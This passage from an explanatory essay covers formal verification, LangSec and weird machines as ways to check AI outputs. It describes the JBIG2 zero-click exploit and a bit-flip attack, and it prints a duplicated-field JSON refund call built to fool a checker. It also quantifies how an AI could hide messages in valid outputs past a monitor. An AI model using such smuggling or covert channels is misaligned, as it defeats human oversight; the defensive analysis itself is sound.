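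The production version of Cedar is a separate program in Rust. Amazon's engineers didn't deploy the Lean model, partly because few programmers know Lean and it lacks many useful libraries. To check that the two programs agree, they use differential testing, which runs randomly generated policies and requests through both and reports any difference. This and related random tests exposed another 21 bugs. But the Rust program could still differ from the proved model on inputs that no test has tried.

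### Cedar policies for agents' tool calls

In December 2025 Amazon introduced Cedar policies for AgentCore, its service for running AI agents. The agents call their tools through a gateway, which checks each call against the policies before passing it on. A policy can refer to the user, the tool and the tool's arguments, so it can, for example, enforce a limit on refunds.

The gateway has no control over tools that the agent can reach some other way. Users can describe a rule in English and have a language model draft the policy. Automated analysis flags drafts that permit too much or contain conditions that no request can meet. It can't determine whether a plausible draft has the limit that the manager intended, so someone still has to read the policy.

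### A verified plan validator and a verified interpreter

Two projects avoid Cedar's split between the proved model and the program that runs. Both use the proof assistant Isabelle, which can generate a working program from definitions proved correct.

In 2018 Mohammad Abdulaziz and Peter Lammich published a validator for plans in a part of PDDL. They defined formally what makes a plan valid and proved that their algorithm accepts exactly the plans that meet this definition. They then used the proof assistant Isabelle to generate the program's core in Standard ML. The proof doesn't cover the parser that reads the plan from a file, so a parsing mistake could make the validator check a different plan from the one the agent will carry out. Abdulaziz and Lukas Koller later developed a verified validator for plans whose actions take time.

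WebAssembly is a compact instruction set that lets browsers and servers run untrusted programs in a sandbox. In 2023 Conrad Watt and colleagues presented WasmRef-Isabelle, a WebAssembly interpreter, and proved that it follows a formal version of the WebAssembly standard. The proof doesn't make every WebAssembly program safe, since a program can still misuse any function its host gives it.

An interpreter is much slower than compiled machine code, so the developers of Wasmtime, a widely used WebAssembly system, use the verified interpreter WasmRef-Isabelle for testing. They run random programs in both systems and investigate any difference in the results. They had given up on similar tests with the official reference interpreter because it was too slow, but WasmRef-Isabelle was fast enough for regular testing. Users' programs still go through Wasmtime's unverified compiler.

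### Verifying an agent framework

A proof can also cover the software that runs an agent. In *Containment Verification* (May 2026), Moon and Varshney describe what they believe is the first such proof for an agent framework. They chose PocketFlow, a minimal framework that runs an agent as a graph of steps.

The proof represents the language model as a method without a body, which may return any action the framework's types allow. Dafny has to verify that the framework obeys its policy for every sequence of these actions. The proof therefore does not depend on the model's training, abilities or intentions.

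Moon and Varshney proved that the framework permits file reads only inside a chosen folder, calls only tools on a list, and stops after a fixed number of steps. They defined an abstract system that obeys these rules, then proved that every step of a more detailed model of the framework matches a permitted step of the abstract one. Dafny translated the verified code into Python. A list of permitted tools is easy to enforce without such a proof, but the proof also shows that no sequence of actions gets around the list.

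The guarantee assumes that the agent can affect the outside world only through these actions. It also assumes that the policy, Dafny, its translation into Python, and the code that turns the model's text into a typed action are all correct. It doesn't cover what a permitted shell tool does.

Language models wrote the specifications and proofs, so the specifications may be too weak. Moon and Varshney had one model write the safety property without seeing the framework's code, so that it couldn't just describe what the code already did. For comparison, they also let a model see the code. When the supplied template didn't fit the agent, that model left a field empty, which made the rule about the field trivially true, just as "every recorded file read is inside the folder" is true if the system never records a read. Dafny accepted the proof, and three additional tests of its quality missed the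 problem.

PocketFlow's interface has only four kinds of action. Moon and Varshney have yet to show that the method works for larger frameworks, which may have dozens.

### Compilers, hardware and the match with reality

A proof about source code doesn't protect against a compiler that translates the code wrongly. In 2011 Xuejun Yang and colleagues at the University of Utah reported that random test programs had exposed more than 325 previously unknown bugs in C compilers. They also tested CompCert, a C compiler with a machine-checked proof, and found errors only in the parts the proof didn't cover. The Linux kernel has a similar weak point because, after the eBPF verifier accepts a program, another component translates it into machine code. Researchers have verified some versions of that component.

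Processors can break a guarantee too. The Spectre attacks, which became public in January 2018, exploit the way a processor predicts the outcome of a branch and runs instructions ahead of time. In the table example, it may predict that r1 is at most 7 and read beyond the table before the comparison finishes. It then discards the result, but the read leaves traces in its cache, and an attacker can recover data by timing later reads. The verifier's ranges were right for the official instruction set, which doesn't describe such traces. Linux developers added countermeasures to the verifier, and the kernel now prevents unprivileged users from loading eBPF programs by default.

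The formal model may also differ from the real system. In 2017 Pedro Fonseca and colleagues examined three distributed systems with machine-checked proofs and found 16 bugs, none of them in the protocols that the proofs covered. Most were in the unverified code connecting the proved part to the network and the disk, and the rest were in the specifications and the verification tools. Moon and Varshney modeled their proof on one of the three systems, IronFleet.

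The shop should therefore concentrate its tests on the code around the checker, which parses the model's text, fetches the customer's records and sends the approved amount to the bank. For example, a test refund of one cent would quickly show whether the interpreter pays out dollars instead of cents.

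## Unintended computation inside restricted formats

A restricted format can allow far more computation than its designers intended. Some formats are Turing-complete by their own rules. Others have simple rules, but a flaw in the software that reads them lets a carefully chosen input put that software into a state its designers never planned for. Later inputs can then control what the software does. Security researchers call such an unintended computer a weird machine. Both problems matter to a gatekeeper because its checks rely on the output language being as simple as it looks.

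### Rewriting rules that may never stop

Transliteration rules convert text from one form to another, such as "é" to "e". The Unicode standard defines a notation for them, and the ICU library applies them in many operating systems and browsers. *Unicode's Transliteration Rules Are Turing-Complete* (Seriot, 2026) proves that this notation can express any computation. This works because a rule can move the cursor back, making the software reapply the rules to text it has just written.

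Seriot's main example works on words made of the letters a, b and c. Each step removes the first two letters and adds others at the end, depending on the first letter removed:

```
a  adds  bc
b  adds  a
c  adds  aaa
```

The process stops when fewer than two letters remain. Three a's develop like this:

```
aaa -> abc -> cbc -> caaa -> aaaaa
```

The three a's have become five. In general, n a's turn into n/2 if n is even and (3n + 1)/2 if n is odd, so 5 leads to 8, 4, 2 and 1, where the process stops. The Collatz conjecture is that it stops from every starting number. With more letters and other rules, the same method can simulate any Turing machine, so no algorithm can determine for every rule file and every text whether the rewriting will end.

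ICU stops each call after 16 rewrites per character of input. The standard sets no limit, and Seriot found two other implementations without one. Ordinary text is harmless because the rules come with the software. But if the shop let its assistant write such rules, it would be accepting programs. Seriot's *Unintended Computations* lists a similar proof for the automation rules in Jira, a project-management tool. A company might well ask an AI to write those rules.

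### Computing with types and playing cards

In C++, a template is a pattern from which the compiler generates code. This one adds up the numbers from 1 to N:

```
template<int N> struct Sum {
    static const int value = N + Sum<N-1>::value;
};
template<> struct Sum<0> {
    static const int value = 0;
};
```

To find `Sum<3>::value`, the compiler needs `Sum<2>`, which needs `Sum<1>`, which needs `Sum<0>`. The second definition supplies 0 for that case, and the compiler works back up to 6 before the program starts. A template that refers to itself acts as a loop, and a special case acts as a branch. Without limits on depth and memory, these are enough for any computation. According to *Template Metaprogramming*, Erwin Unruh first demonstrated the technique at a C++ committee meeting, with code that made the compiler print prime numbers in its error messages.

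The card game Magic: The Gathering is Turing-complete too. Churchill, Biderman and Herrick (2019), in *Magic*, built a Turing machine from its cards. Such a machine has a tape of symbols, a head that reads one symbol at a time, and rules for what to write and which way to move. One step works like this:

1. Each cell of the tape is a creature. Its type, such as Elf or Sliver, stands for the symbol. Its toughness gives its distance from the head, starting at 2, and its colour shows which side it is on.
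2. A player casts a spell that lowers every creature's toughness by 2, which kills only the creature under the head.
3. Another card reacts to the dead creature's type. If an Aetherborn dies, for example, the card creates a white Sliver, which writes a new symbol and makes the head move left.
4. One spell adds 2 to the toughness of the creatures on the side the head is leaving, and another subtracts 1 from all of them. Each creature's toughness then matches its new distance from the head.

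The game's rules force every move, and the first player wins if and only if the machine halts, so no algorithm can predict the winner of every such game. Each card's text is short and easy to understand, but the computation comes from how the cards interact. A checker that inspects the rules in an output one by one can therefore miss it.

Computation can also happen outside the part of a system that a checker inspects. In *The Page-Fault Weird Machine*, Bangert, Bratus and colleagues made an Intel processor compute without completing a single instruction. When a program uses an invalid memory address, the processor looks in tables for the code that should respond. If the tables send it to another invalid address, it keeps responding to new errors, and each response changes numbers in memory. They combined these changes into a single operation, which subtracts 1 from a number or jumps elsewhere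 if the number is already zero. Repeating that operation is enough for any computation. Every table entry was well-formed, and a checker for instructions would have had none to inspect.

### Dullien's account of weird machines

Dullien's *Weird machines, exploitability, and provable unexploitability* explains how flawed software turns into a weird machine. It starts with the intended finite-state machine, the program as its designer imagines it. Dullien's example is a server that stores up to 5,000 password-secret pairs. When someone sends a stored password, the server returns the matching secret and deletes the pair. The security requirement is that an attacker can't do better than guess passwords.

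The programmer has to imitate this machine on a general-purpose computer, whose memory can be in vastly more states. Dullien divides them into three groups:

- Sane states correspond to a state of the intended machine.
- Transitory states occur briefly on the way from one sane state to the next.
- Weird states are all the others, and they correspond to nothing in the design.

A bug or a hardware fault can put a computer into a "weird state", in which the program keeps applying its normal operations to data that no longer makes sense. Since each input triggers an operation, an attacker who chooses the inputs is in effect programming a machine that nobody designed. Dullien defines an exploit as a program for this machine that breaks a security requirement.

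Dullien compares two versions of the server, facing an attacker who may pause it at any moment and flip one bit of its memory outside the processor's registers. The faster version stores its data as a linked list, where each record consists of a password, a secret and the address of the next record. Suppose the attacker's record (p, s, n) comes just before the victim's (P, S, N). By flipping a bit in an earlier address, the attacker shifts the place where the program expects a record to begin:

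```
before:   [p  s  n] [P  S  N]
after:     p [s  n  P] S  N
```

The attacker now sends s as if it were a password. The program finds s at the start of the shifted record, returns n and deletes the record. To delete it, the program writes the address of a free slot into the third cell, overwriting the victim's password. The attacker can work out that address, send it as the password and receive the victim's secret.

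The slower version keeps the pairs in a plain array and searches it from the beginning each time, so its data contains no addresses to corrupt. Dullien proved that anything an attacker can do to this version by flipping one bit can also be done without the flip in at most 10,000 extra exchanges. There are more than four billion possible passwords, so 10,000 extra guesses barely improve the attacker's chances. The proof covers only a single flipped bit, but it shows that two programs with the same specification can differ greatly in how much damage one fault allows.

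In both versions, the program runs only its own instructions in their normal order, so a defence that checks for diverted execution would not detect the attack. Dullien recommends defences that detect corrupted data and stop the program quickly. The shop's interpreter should do the same, and it should use simple, fixed data layouts where practical.

### The JBIG2 attack

A real attack in 2021 combined a software flaw with a format whose operations were unusually flexible. Beer and Groß (2021), of Google's security research team Project Zero, analysed an exploit by the spyware company NSO Group that targeted a Saudi activist. The exploit arrived through Apple's iMessage and worked without the activist tapping anything.

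The exploit used JBIG2, a format for compressing black-and-white scans. A JBIG2 file can store the shape of a letter once, and the decoder draws it wherever the letter appears. To correct small differences between the copies, the decoder combines images pixel by pixel using logical operations such as AND and XOR. The decoder carries out a list of drawing commands in a single pass, and the format has no scripts.

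In a correct decoder, these operations can change only the image. The iPhone's decoder contained an arithmetic error that let a crafted file apply them to other parts of memory. Since AND and XOR are enough to build any digital circuit, the attackers wrote more than 70,000 commands that formed a small computer, with registers and a 64-bit adder. While the phone decoded the image, this computer did the calculations needed for the next stage of the attack. The lack of loops didn't prevent this, because the attackers could write out as many commands as they needed. Apple fixed the error in September 2021.

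This part of iMessage also accepted many formats besides the animated GIFs Apple had intended it for. The software ignored the file's name and inferred the format from its contents, so a file with a name ending in ".gif" could reach the decoders for more than 20 formats, some of them obscure. Apple later removed this route.

Attackers can sometimes exploit a parser without building a computer from the format's features. Google Project Zero's *An analysis of the NSO BLASTPASS iMessage exploit* (2025) describes a later attack that did this through the image format WebP. The analyst at first expected another weird machine, but calls that guess "completely wrong". A narrow format limits what an attacker can do with a parser's bug, but the parser still has to be correct.

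### Language-theoretic security

Language-theoretic security, or LangSec, is a research programme that tackles these problems by restricting the languages that software reads. Len Sassaman, Meredith Patterson, Sergey Bratus and Michael Locasto set out its foundations in *Security Applications of Formal Language Theory*. They recommend the least powerful input language that meets the need, ideally a regular language (one a finite automaton can recognise) or a context-free one. They also recommend that software check that the whole input belongs to the language before acting on any part of it, and that the sending and receiving programs interpret it identically.

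An interpreter that carries out a refund plan while still reading it may pay out before it reaches a malformed step. Differences between programs can be just as costly, as with this call:

```
{"tool": "refund", "order": 4417,
 "amount_cents": 8000, "amount_cents": 500000}
```

Some JSON parsers keep the first of two fields with the same name, and others keep the last. If an output sets the amount field to 80 dollars and then to 5,000, a checker that keeps the first value approves 80 dollars, but an interpreter that keeps the last has the shop pay out 5,000.

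No algorithm can determine, for every pair of context-free grammars, whether both describe the same texts, so LangSec researchers favour the deterministic ones. A parser for a deterministic context-free language has only one rule to apply at each step, so each text has exactly one structure. An algorithm can also determine whether two such parsers accept the same texts.

In *AI Security is a LangSec Problem*, von Hippel and Miyazono apply these ideas to language models. They warn that developers extend the parsers for model output piecemeal in response to demand, and run them without isolating them from the rest of the application. An attacker who can influence the model can try to make it write text that exploits a bug in the parser. They also describe configuration files with hidden Unicode characters, which look harmless to a person but contain instructions that an AI coding tool follows.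 A human reviewer therefore has to see the same content as the machine.

O'Connor (2026), in *CBCL*, presents a message language for AI agents that follows LangSec's principles. It has eight basic message types, and agents can teach each other new ones by sending templates that expand into the basic types. Each new template must pass three checks:

- It may not refer to itself, directly or through other templates.
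- It must declare limits within fixed maximums, including 64 levels of nesting and 8,192 characters of expanded text.
- It may not redefine a basic type.

The software expands each template once and never reprocesses the result, so it lacks the feature that made transliteration rules Turing-complete. O'Connor proved in Lean that the language remains deterministic and context-free when such templates are added. In one test, the checker rejected a template called `bomb` that expanded into two copies of itself.

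These restrictions also rule out useful operations. A CBCL template can't add up the items on an invoice, compute a checksum over other fields, or verify that a reply belongs to an earlier message. Application code has to do this work, and the proof doesn't cover that code or what tools do with a message. CBCL messages can still contain free text, including prompt injections.

### What Turing-completeness does and doesn't give an attacker

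A Turing-complete format can perform any computation, but computation alone doesn't open a file or send an email. A game of Magic, for example, can't read a hard disk. LangSec researchers accept this. In *Page Fault Liberation Army*, Bratus and Bangert (2013) noted that Turing completeness only describes which computations are possible, and wished for a scale "better suited to exploit power". Bangert and colleagues describe their page-fault computer as neither a vulnerability nor an exploit. Dullien's linked-list example also shows that an attack doesn't always need a general-purpose computer, since the attacker there needed only a few inputs.

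For a gatekeeper, the bigger problem is that Turing-completeness defeats checks made in advance. *Why does a Turing-complete type system make type checking undecidable?* (2017) discusses Radu Grigore's proof that Java's rules for generic types can express any computation. Grigore first concluded that all Java type checkers must have bugs, but later claimed only that a type checker that never gives a wrong answer can't be guaranteed to finish on every program. If the gatekeeper uses a compiler as its checker, an AI could write a program that makes the compiler run forever.

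The shop can stop the compiler after a while and reject the program, which is sound, but it has to limit total steps or time. A limit on how deeply templates nest would not have stopped a short program by Todd Veldhuizen, reproduced in *C++ templates are turing complete* (2005). Its templates are nested only 16 levels deep, far below the 1,024 levels that the C++ standard recommends compilers support. Each template needs five new ones at the next level, so the last level alone has 5^16, or about 153 billion. Compiling the program took more than 24 hours on a two-processor machine.

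Hidden computation also makes other flaws easier to exploit. *Surprisingly Turing-Complete*, an online catalogue of systems that allow such computation, points out that many flaws are hard to exploit blindly. An attacker who can run a program inside the target can use it to examine the target first and work out what to do, as the attackers did with the JBIG2 computer.

The next program in a chain can also provide access. *Weird Machine Compositors* (2026) warns that two processing stages can each be correct and still form a weird machine together. For example, one stage might insert a customer's name into a message, and the next might run any formulas in that message. A customer who enters a formula as their name then controls the second stage. The danger arises because the first stage's output doesn't show that part of it came from a stranger. A checker therefore has to examine the text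 that the last stage will run.

### What a valid output can still carry

An output that passes every check can still contain a hidden message. If an AI can choose among N equally valid outputs, its choice can convey up to log₂ N bits to a reader who knows how to decode it. The maximum is one bit for two outputs and ten bits for 1,024. The amount is lower if the AI can't choose freely or the reader can't tell some of the outputs apart.

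The earlier count of about 11 bits for a refund call covered the choice of order, amount and reason. JSON allows further choices that don't affect the refund at all. This call can list its three fields in six different orders:

```
{"tool":"refund","order":4417,"amount_cents":8000}
```

It also has 12 places between symbols where a space is optional. That makes 6 × 2^12 = 24,576 ways to write the same refund, which can carry about 14.6 bits, more than the choice of refund itself carries. Four such calls could carry a 16-digit card number. If the format allows several spaces in a row, only the maximum text length limits how much a call can carry.

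Programs leave even more room. If an AI picks each of 20 variable names from 1,000 plausible words, the names can carry about 200 bits. Comments and free-form strings add several bits per character, and readers expect ordinary language there.

A message hidden in the spaces needs a recipient. It reaches nobody if the interpreter discards the text after moving the money, but it may reach a reader the shop never considered if the text goes into a public code repository or a log that another AI agent reads.

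### Canonical forms

A canonical form is a single permitted spelling for each meaning. For refund calls, it could require fields in alphabetical order, with no spaces, repeated fields or leading zeros. The checker can reject every other spelling, or it can extract the values from the model's text and write a new call from them. The second method is usually better because it lets the model write in its usual style, and models can do much worse when a mask blocks even a small habit, such as putting a space before an equals sign. The checker then passes on only the new call, not the model's original text.

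Rewriting the call removes all 14.6 bits from the spelling. It also prevents the dispute over repeated fields, since the interpreter receives a call with only one amount. Canonical forms have long been useful for digital signatures, which fail if a single byte changes. CBCL's signatures use a standard one that puts each string's length before the string. O'Connor acknowledges that programs may still differ in details such as Unicode. An "é", for instance, can be one character or an "e" followed by a separate accent.

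A canonical form can't remove the information in a choice that matters. If the assistant may refund either 79 or 80 dollars, the amount can still carry one bit of information. The shop could reduce this by allowing only multiples of 10 dollars, but then it could no longer refund the exact price of most goods.

Canonical forms have a bigger drawback for programs, because deleting comments and renaming variables to v1, v2 and v3 removes the explanations a human reviewer needs along with hidden messages. The shop could keep the original for the reviewer and send only the stripped version onward, but it would then have to make sure both versions do the same thing.

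Richer languages also make it harder to define one spelling per meaning. Every finite automaton has a unique smallest version, which can serve as its canonical form. In a Turing-complete language, no algorithm can find a canonical form for every program, because comparing these forms would show whether any two programs behave the same way, which is undecidable. A formatter can standardise the layout but may leave `8000` and `4000 + 4000` as two spellings of the same value.

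A tool can instead reject whatever it can't standardise. The compiler for Apple's language Swift does this with some declarations about types, according to a forum discussion titled *BrainF\*\*\* in the Swift type system*. It rejects such a declaration unless it can work out a complete set of rewriting rules for it, which would let it reduce any expression to a normal form in a finite number of steps. Some of the declarations it rejects would have been harmless.

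### Tests for a new output language

Before the shop lets its assistant write in a new language, it can run these tests:

1. Search the language's definition for signs of hidden computation. *Surprisingly Turing-Complete* lists text substitution, search and replace, values that depend on their neighbours, and operations whose running time is hard to predict. Substitution is especially risky if the software processes its own results again.
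2. Ask a skilled programmer to build a loop or a logic gate from the permitted features. If this succeeds, treat the language as a programming language. A failed attempt proves little, so a language for important actions needs a proof that every output finishes.
3. Give the checker short inputs that are designed to take as long as possible. Limit the total time, memory and output size as well as the depth of nesting.
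4. Find out what the software accepts in practice. Send it repeated fields, extra text after the end, unusual characters and files in other formats, and compare how the checker and the interpreter read them.
5. Put an error at the very end of a long output and confirm that nothing has taken effect when the checker finds it.
6. Take one action and count the texts that produce it. If there is more than one, have the checker rewrite them all in the same form, then count again.
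7. Repeat the tests whenever someone adds a feature. If the shop needs invoice totals, for example, it can add one tool that calculates them instead of adding loops to the language.

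## Which AI outputs fit a checkable language

The shop can design an output language for refunds because it knows what a refund is. People also want theorems, driving decisions, diagnoses and essays from AI, and a checker can establish far more about some of these than about others. Mathematics is the best case because mathematicians can write out a statement completely in a formal language, and nothing outside the text affects whether it is true.

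### What a Lean proof lets a reader check

A theorem in the proof assistant Lean has two parts, as in this example:

```
theorem even_sum (a b : ℕ) (ha : Even a) (hb : Even b) :
    Even (a + b) := ha.add hb
```

Everything before `:=` is the statement that the sum of two even numbers is even. The rest is the proof, which here is a reference to a fact in Mathlib, Lean's main mathematics library. A small program called the kernel checks that each step follows from Lean's axioms and earlier results. A reader who trusts the kernel and understands the statement can skip the proof, however long it is and whoever wrote it.

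On 20 November 2026 Levent Alpöge, a mathematician at Anthropic, released a Lean proof of the Riemann hypothesis that he had made with the company's AI, Claude. It has 17 million lines. The hypothesis dates from 1859 and concerns the zeta function, whose zeros govern how the prime numbers are distributed. In Mathlib, its statement amounts to this:

```
for all complex s:
    zeta(s) = 0  and  s ≠ 1  and  s not in {-2, -4, -6, ...}
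    implies  Re(s) = 1/2
```

The Lean and Mathlib communities certified the proof the next day. The Lean community blog's *Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026) gives four grounds:

1. Experts in Lean and number theory had carefully vetted the statement, which was already in Mathlib.
2. Dozens of people compiled Alpöge's files without errors and got the same exported proof.
3. Two independent tools confirmed that the theorem he proved is exactly Mathlib's statement.
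4. Several proof checkers, written in different programming languages, accepted the exported proof.

Only vetting the statement took mathematical judgement. Computers did the rest, and anyone with a large enough machine can repeat their work. Sutherland (2026), in *Verification files for the Lean proof of the Riemann Hypothesis*, also confirmed that the main theorems depend only on Lean's three standard axioms, so the proof doesn't assume what it should prove.

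The vetting matters because a small mistake can change what a statement means. Artificial Wasteland's *The Twenty Lines* removes the clauses one at a time. Without the exception for -2, -4, -6 and so on, the statement is false, because zeta is 0 at all of those numbers. The statement also makes an exception for 1. Zeta has no value there, but every function in Lean needs a value everywhere, so Mathlib's definition assigns it one, about -0.977. That definition comes from the project that Loeffler and Stoll (2025) describe in *Formalizing zeta and L-functions in Lean*. Loeffler's first version of the hypothesis lacked the exception for 1, and two other mathematicians pointed out the problem. Without it, the formal statement would have been false if the arbitrary value had happened to be 0, for a reason unrelated to prime numbers.

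Lean's creator, de Moura (2026), writes in *Lean Now Ships with Verified Kernels* that AI agents have become good at finding faults in Lean's kernel, which is part of the trusted base. The developers have since added a checker called con-leche. Claude wrote it under heavy human supervision, along with a proof that con-leche can't accept a false theorem if set theory is consistent. Breitner, who supervised the work, has not yet seen an AI agent try to exploit a bug in Lean without being asked to (*Riemann con leche*, 2026).

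### Mathematics without proof code

Most mathematics that AI produces still lacks such a guarantee. In October 2026 OpenAI released 722 mathematics papers by one of its models, and only about 45 per cent came with Lean code, according to Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026). OpenAI has retracted three papers because of a sign error, and none of them had Lean code.

Lean code doesn't always cover a paper's main result either. For around 38 of the 290 theorems with code, the code didn't even state the main theorem. For example, one paper is about Lech's multiplicity conjecture, an algebra problem that had been open since 1960, but its Lean code proves only a corollary. Xena suspects that OpenAI published before it had finished some of the formal proofs. The 45 per cent figure therefore probably reflects how much of the work was finished rather than how much mathematics Lean can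 express.

Some statements are also hard to read. The Riemann hypothesis fits on a line or two because Mathlib already defines the zeta function. A formal statement of the Hodge conjecture currently needs more than 10,000 lines of definitions beyond those in Mathlib, and a mistake in any of them could change the statement's meaning.

The share of mathematics that is checked will probably grow. Taylor's *Lean for the working mathematician* (2026) explains how any mathematician with a subscription to a leading AI model can verify their own papers. But Avigad, Buzzard and colleagues warn in *How to Formalize All of Mathematics* (2026) that formalizing everything as fast as possible would probably do lasting damage.

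### Exporting what AI has learned

In *Provably Safe AI*, MIT physicist Max Tegmark (2025) proposes extending this method far beyond mathematics. People would stop deploying their most powerful neural networks and use them to write software instead. A person writes the specification, the AI writes the program and a proof that it meets the specification, and a proof checker of about 300 lines of code checks the proof. Tegmark argues that if a scientist invented a new way to steer a rocket, we would ask for the algorithm and verify it rather than put the scientist in the cockpit.

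This works only for knowledge that an AI can turn into code. Tegmark notes that cats can't write down anything they know, while people can write down a modest part, and conjectures that the share grows with intelligence. There is little evidence so far. In an earlier talk, also called *Provably Safe AI*, Tegmark described what he called a toy example, in which software extracted an addition algorithm from a trained network, rewrote it in Python and proved in Dafny that it adds all numbers correctly.

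Zac Hatfield-Dodds, who maintains a widely used software-testing library, doubts that the approach can replace general AI. In the talk *Formal Verification is Overrated*, Hatfield-Dodds argues that some tasks will always be left to neural networks because explicit software won't outperform machine learning at what machine learning does best. In translation, for example, decades of handwritten rules never matched what networks learned from text. Tegmark's conjecture is a reply to this argument, but nobody has tested the conjecture on a task like translation.

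*Provably safe systems* (Tegmark and Omohundro, 2023) had proposed a larger plan, in which chips would run only programs with a valid safety proof, and drones and DNA synthesis machines would require one to operate. No AI, however intelligent, can prove a false theorem, so Tegmark and Omohundro considered proof the only method that guarantees control. They expected that the programs people deploy would generally not be neural networks, whose inner workings are too messy to verify.

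ARIA was more selective about tasks in its original thesis for the Safeguarded AI programme. It sought problems that scientists already understand and can measure, and whose outcomes don't depend on tiny differences in starting conditions. Balancing an electricity grid qualifies because the difficulty lies mainly in the number of components. The thesis also listed supply chains, mobile phone networks and clinical trials.

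### Can a proof cover the physical world?

Andrew Dickson made the most detailed criticism in *Limitations on Formal Verification for AI Safety* (2024), where he argues that proofs apply to systems of symbols and not to the world. Engineers used formal verification on the software that landed the Perseverance rover on Mars in 2021. This showed that the program was free of certain internal faults, but not that the rover would land safely. About half of all Mars missions have failed, and by one analysis software accounts for only about a fifth of the risk.

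Nora Ammann, who later took over ARIA's programme, answered Dickson and other critics in *In response to critiques of Guaranteed Safe AI* (2025). The model doesn't have to predict exactly what will happen, Ammann argues, as long as it allows for everything that could. A model that says only that a temperature will stay below 50 degrees can be correct without giving the temperature. The argument needs two inclusions:

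```
what can really happen  ⊆  what the model allows  ⊆  what is safe
```

A verifier can prove that everything the model allows is safe. No proof can establish that the model allows everything that can really happen, but measurements can support that scientific claim. Ammann therefore adds a monitor that compares measurements with the model and hands control to a simpler backup system if they disagree. A critic replied below the essay that monitoring would be pointless if there were a real guarantee. The critic is right that the guarantee is conditional, but the monitor is useful because it checks for the errors that the proof can't exclude.

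In DNA synthesis, the choice of property affects both how hard a sequence is to check and which dangers the check covers. Dickson takes the property to be "this sequence can't harm people", and argues that proving it would require simulating the whole human body over years. In 2022 the most advanced simulation covered 20 minutes in the life of one very simple cell. Ammann proposes a narrower property, that a virus can't enter human cells. A checker would compare each protein of the virus with each protein on the surface of human cells and reject the sequence if any pair might let the virus in. Ammann concedes that this is beyond current capabilities. The checker would also reject some useful gene therapies, and it would miss other dangers that Dickson mentions, such as someone inserting a harmful sequence directly into a cell's DNA.

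An even narrower check compares each order with a list of known pathogens. Software can do that today, but the check gives no protection against a pathogen that isn't on the list.

Dickson also asks how a buyer would know that the machine in the laboratory is the one the proof describes. Outsiders can rerun a Lean proof but can't confirm that a chatbot on a remote server matches its certificate. Ammann proposes solving this with cryptographic signatures and tamper-resistant hardware, which buyers would also have to trust.

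### Advice and persuasion

The two sides largely agree that the approach doesn't suit conversation. Dickson writes that to prove a chatbot's answer won't misinform anyone, its developers would have to model the minds of readers they can't identify, since the user may post the answer online or put it in a speech. Ammann accepts that the approach isn't promising for chatbots, because natural language is too open. The approach also fits badly wherever the outcome depends on what particular individuals do. A doctor, for example, has to advise one patient, whereas a grid operator can predict the demand of a million households without knowing when any one of them will boil a kettle.

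Ammann proposes limiting what an AI can communicate if it might manipulate people. The AI would submit an answer to a precisely defined problem, with proofs that the answer is correct and that no other correct answer exists. Its only choice would be whether to answer, which conveys at most one bit. This could work for finding the cheapest delivery route, if there is only one, but it can't work for writing an essay, because there are countless ways to write a good one.

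Another commenter asked what fraction of economically valuable work would allow such proofs, which nobody has measured. ARIA's original thesis assumed, in a diagram, that AI with quantitative guarantees would reach about 20 per cent of the economic value of unconstrained AI if the programme succeeded. The figure was an input to a simplified model of how governments might cooperate, but it suggests that even the programme's founders expected most of the value to be out of reach of AI with such guarantees.

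### Properties that nobody can state

Some properties are hard to define even when all the facts are known. Dickson gives the example of a genuine photograph that misleads because someone shows it out of context. A rule against false images would allow the photograph, so blocking it would take a rule against misleading images, which would need a definition of "misleading".

Ammann replies that a specification can name particular states to avoid, such as an overloaded power line, without capturing everything people value, and that AI can help by finding cases that the draft rules handle badly. Tegmark and Omohundro likewise suggest starting with requirements that people can already write down, such as "nobody gets into this computer without valid credentials". These replies work for power lines and computers but not for the photograph, and even the rule about credentials would let in a thief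 with a stolen password.

Dickson expected AI to become good at finding proofs but not at building models and specifications, at least not soon enough to matter. AI has since become good at finding proofs, but it still does much worse on programming tasks when it has to write the specification itself.

### Sorting outputs by two questions

To judge whether a gatekeeper can handle a kind of output, a designer can ask whether the output has a formal syntax and whether anyone can state the desired property in formal terms.

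| Output | Formal syntax? | Can people state the property they want? |
|---|---|---|
| Mathematical proof | Yes | Yes, as the theorem |
| Access policy | Yes | Yes, once managers decide who may do what |
| Control code | Yes | Yes for software faults; for physical safety, only relative to a model |
| Database query | Yes | Yes for permissions; rarely for "answers my question" |
| Medical advice | Only in parts, such as a prescription | Yes for dose limits; no for "best for this patient" |
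| Essay | Only in parts, such as references | Yes for "this source exists"; no for "fair" or "worth reading" |

Database queries show that a formal syntax isn't enough. Suppose a manager at the shop asks how many orders arrived late, and the AI writes:

```
SELECT COUNT(*) FROM orders WHERE shipped_on > due_on;
```

A checker can confirm that the query reads only the orders table and changes nothing. But the query counts only orders that left the warehouse late, so it misses those that left on time and were delayed in the post. To catch this error, the checker would need a formal version of the manager's question. That version would itself be a correct query, so anyone who could supply it wouldn't need the AI's.

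### Checking the formal part of advice and essays

If only part of an output fits a checkable language, a checker can still test that part. In medical advice, it may be the prescription. If a drug's limit is 60 milligrams a day per kilogram of body weight, a child who weighs 20 kilograms can take up to 1,200 milligrams a day, so the checker would accept four daily doses of 250 milligrams but reject four of 500. It can also compare the drug with the child's allergies and other medicines, but it can't verify the diagnosis.

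Hospitals have long run checks like these on doctors' electronic prescriptions, and false alarms can lead clinicians to dismiss the warnings. In a 2006 review, Heleen van der Sijs and colleagues found that clinicians overrode 49 to 96 per cent of drug safety alerts.

Amazon applies a similar idea to chatbots that answer questions about rules, such as a company's leave policy. Its Automated Reasoning checks, released in 2025, turn the policy into logical formulas and the chatbot's answer into structured claims. A solver then tests whether the claims follow from the policy. The solver is reliable, but the language model that translates the answer can make mistakes.

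References are the easiest part of an essay to check. In 2023 a federal judge in New York fined two lawyers and their firm $5,000 over a brief that cited court cases ChatGPT had invented. A program could have looked up each case in a database and found that it didn't exist. A program can also compare quotations with their sources word by word.

It is harder to check whether a real source supports the sentence that cites it, because someone has to understand both. In 2023, Nelson Liu, Tianyi Zhang and Percy Liang had people check answers from four AI search engines, and found that citations fully supported only 51.5 per cent of the sentences. Sewon Min and colleagues automated part of this work the same year with FActScore, which splits a text into short factual claims and has a language model compare each one with Wikipedia. This makes mistakes easier to find, but the verdict is again a model's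 prediction, so the check is not sound.

Even a perfect check of every claim would not reveal what the writer omitted. An essay can accurately cite five trials in which a drug worked and never mention the ten in which it failed.
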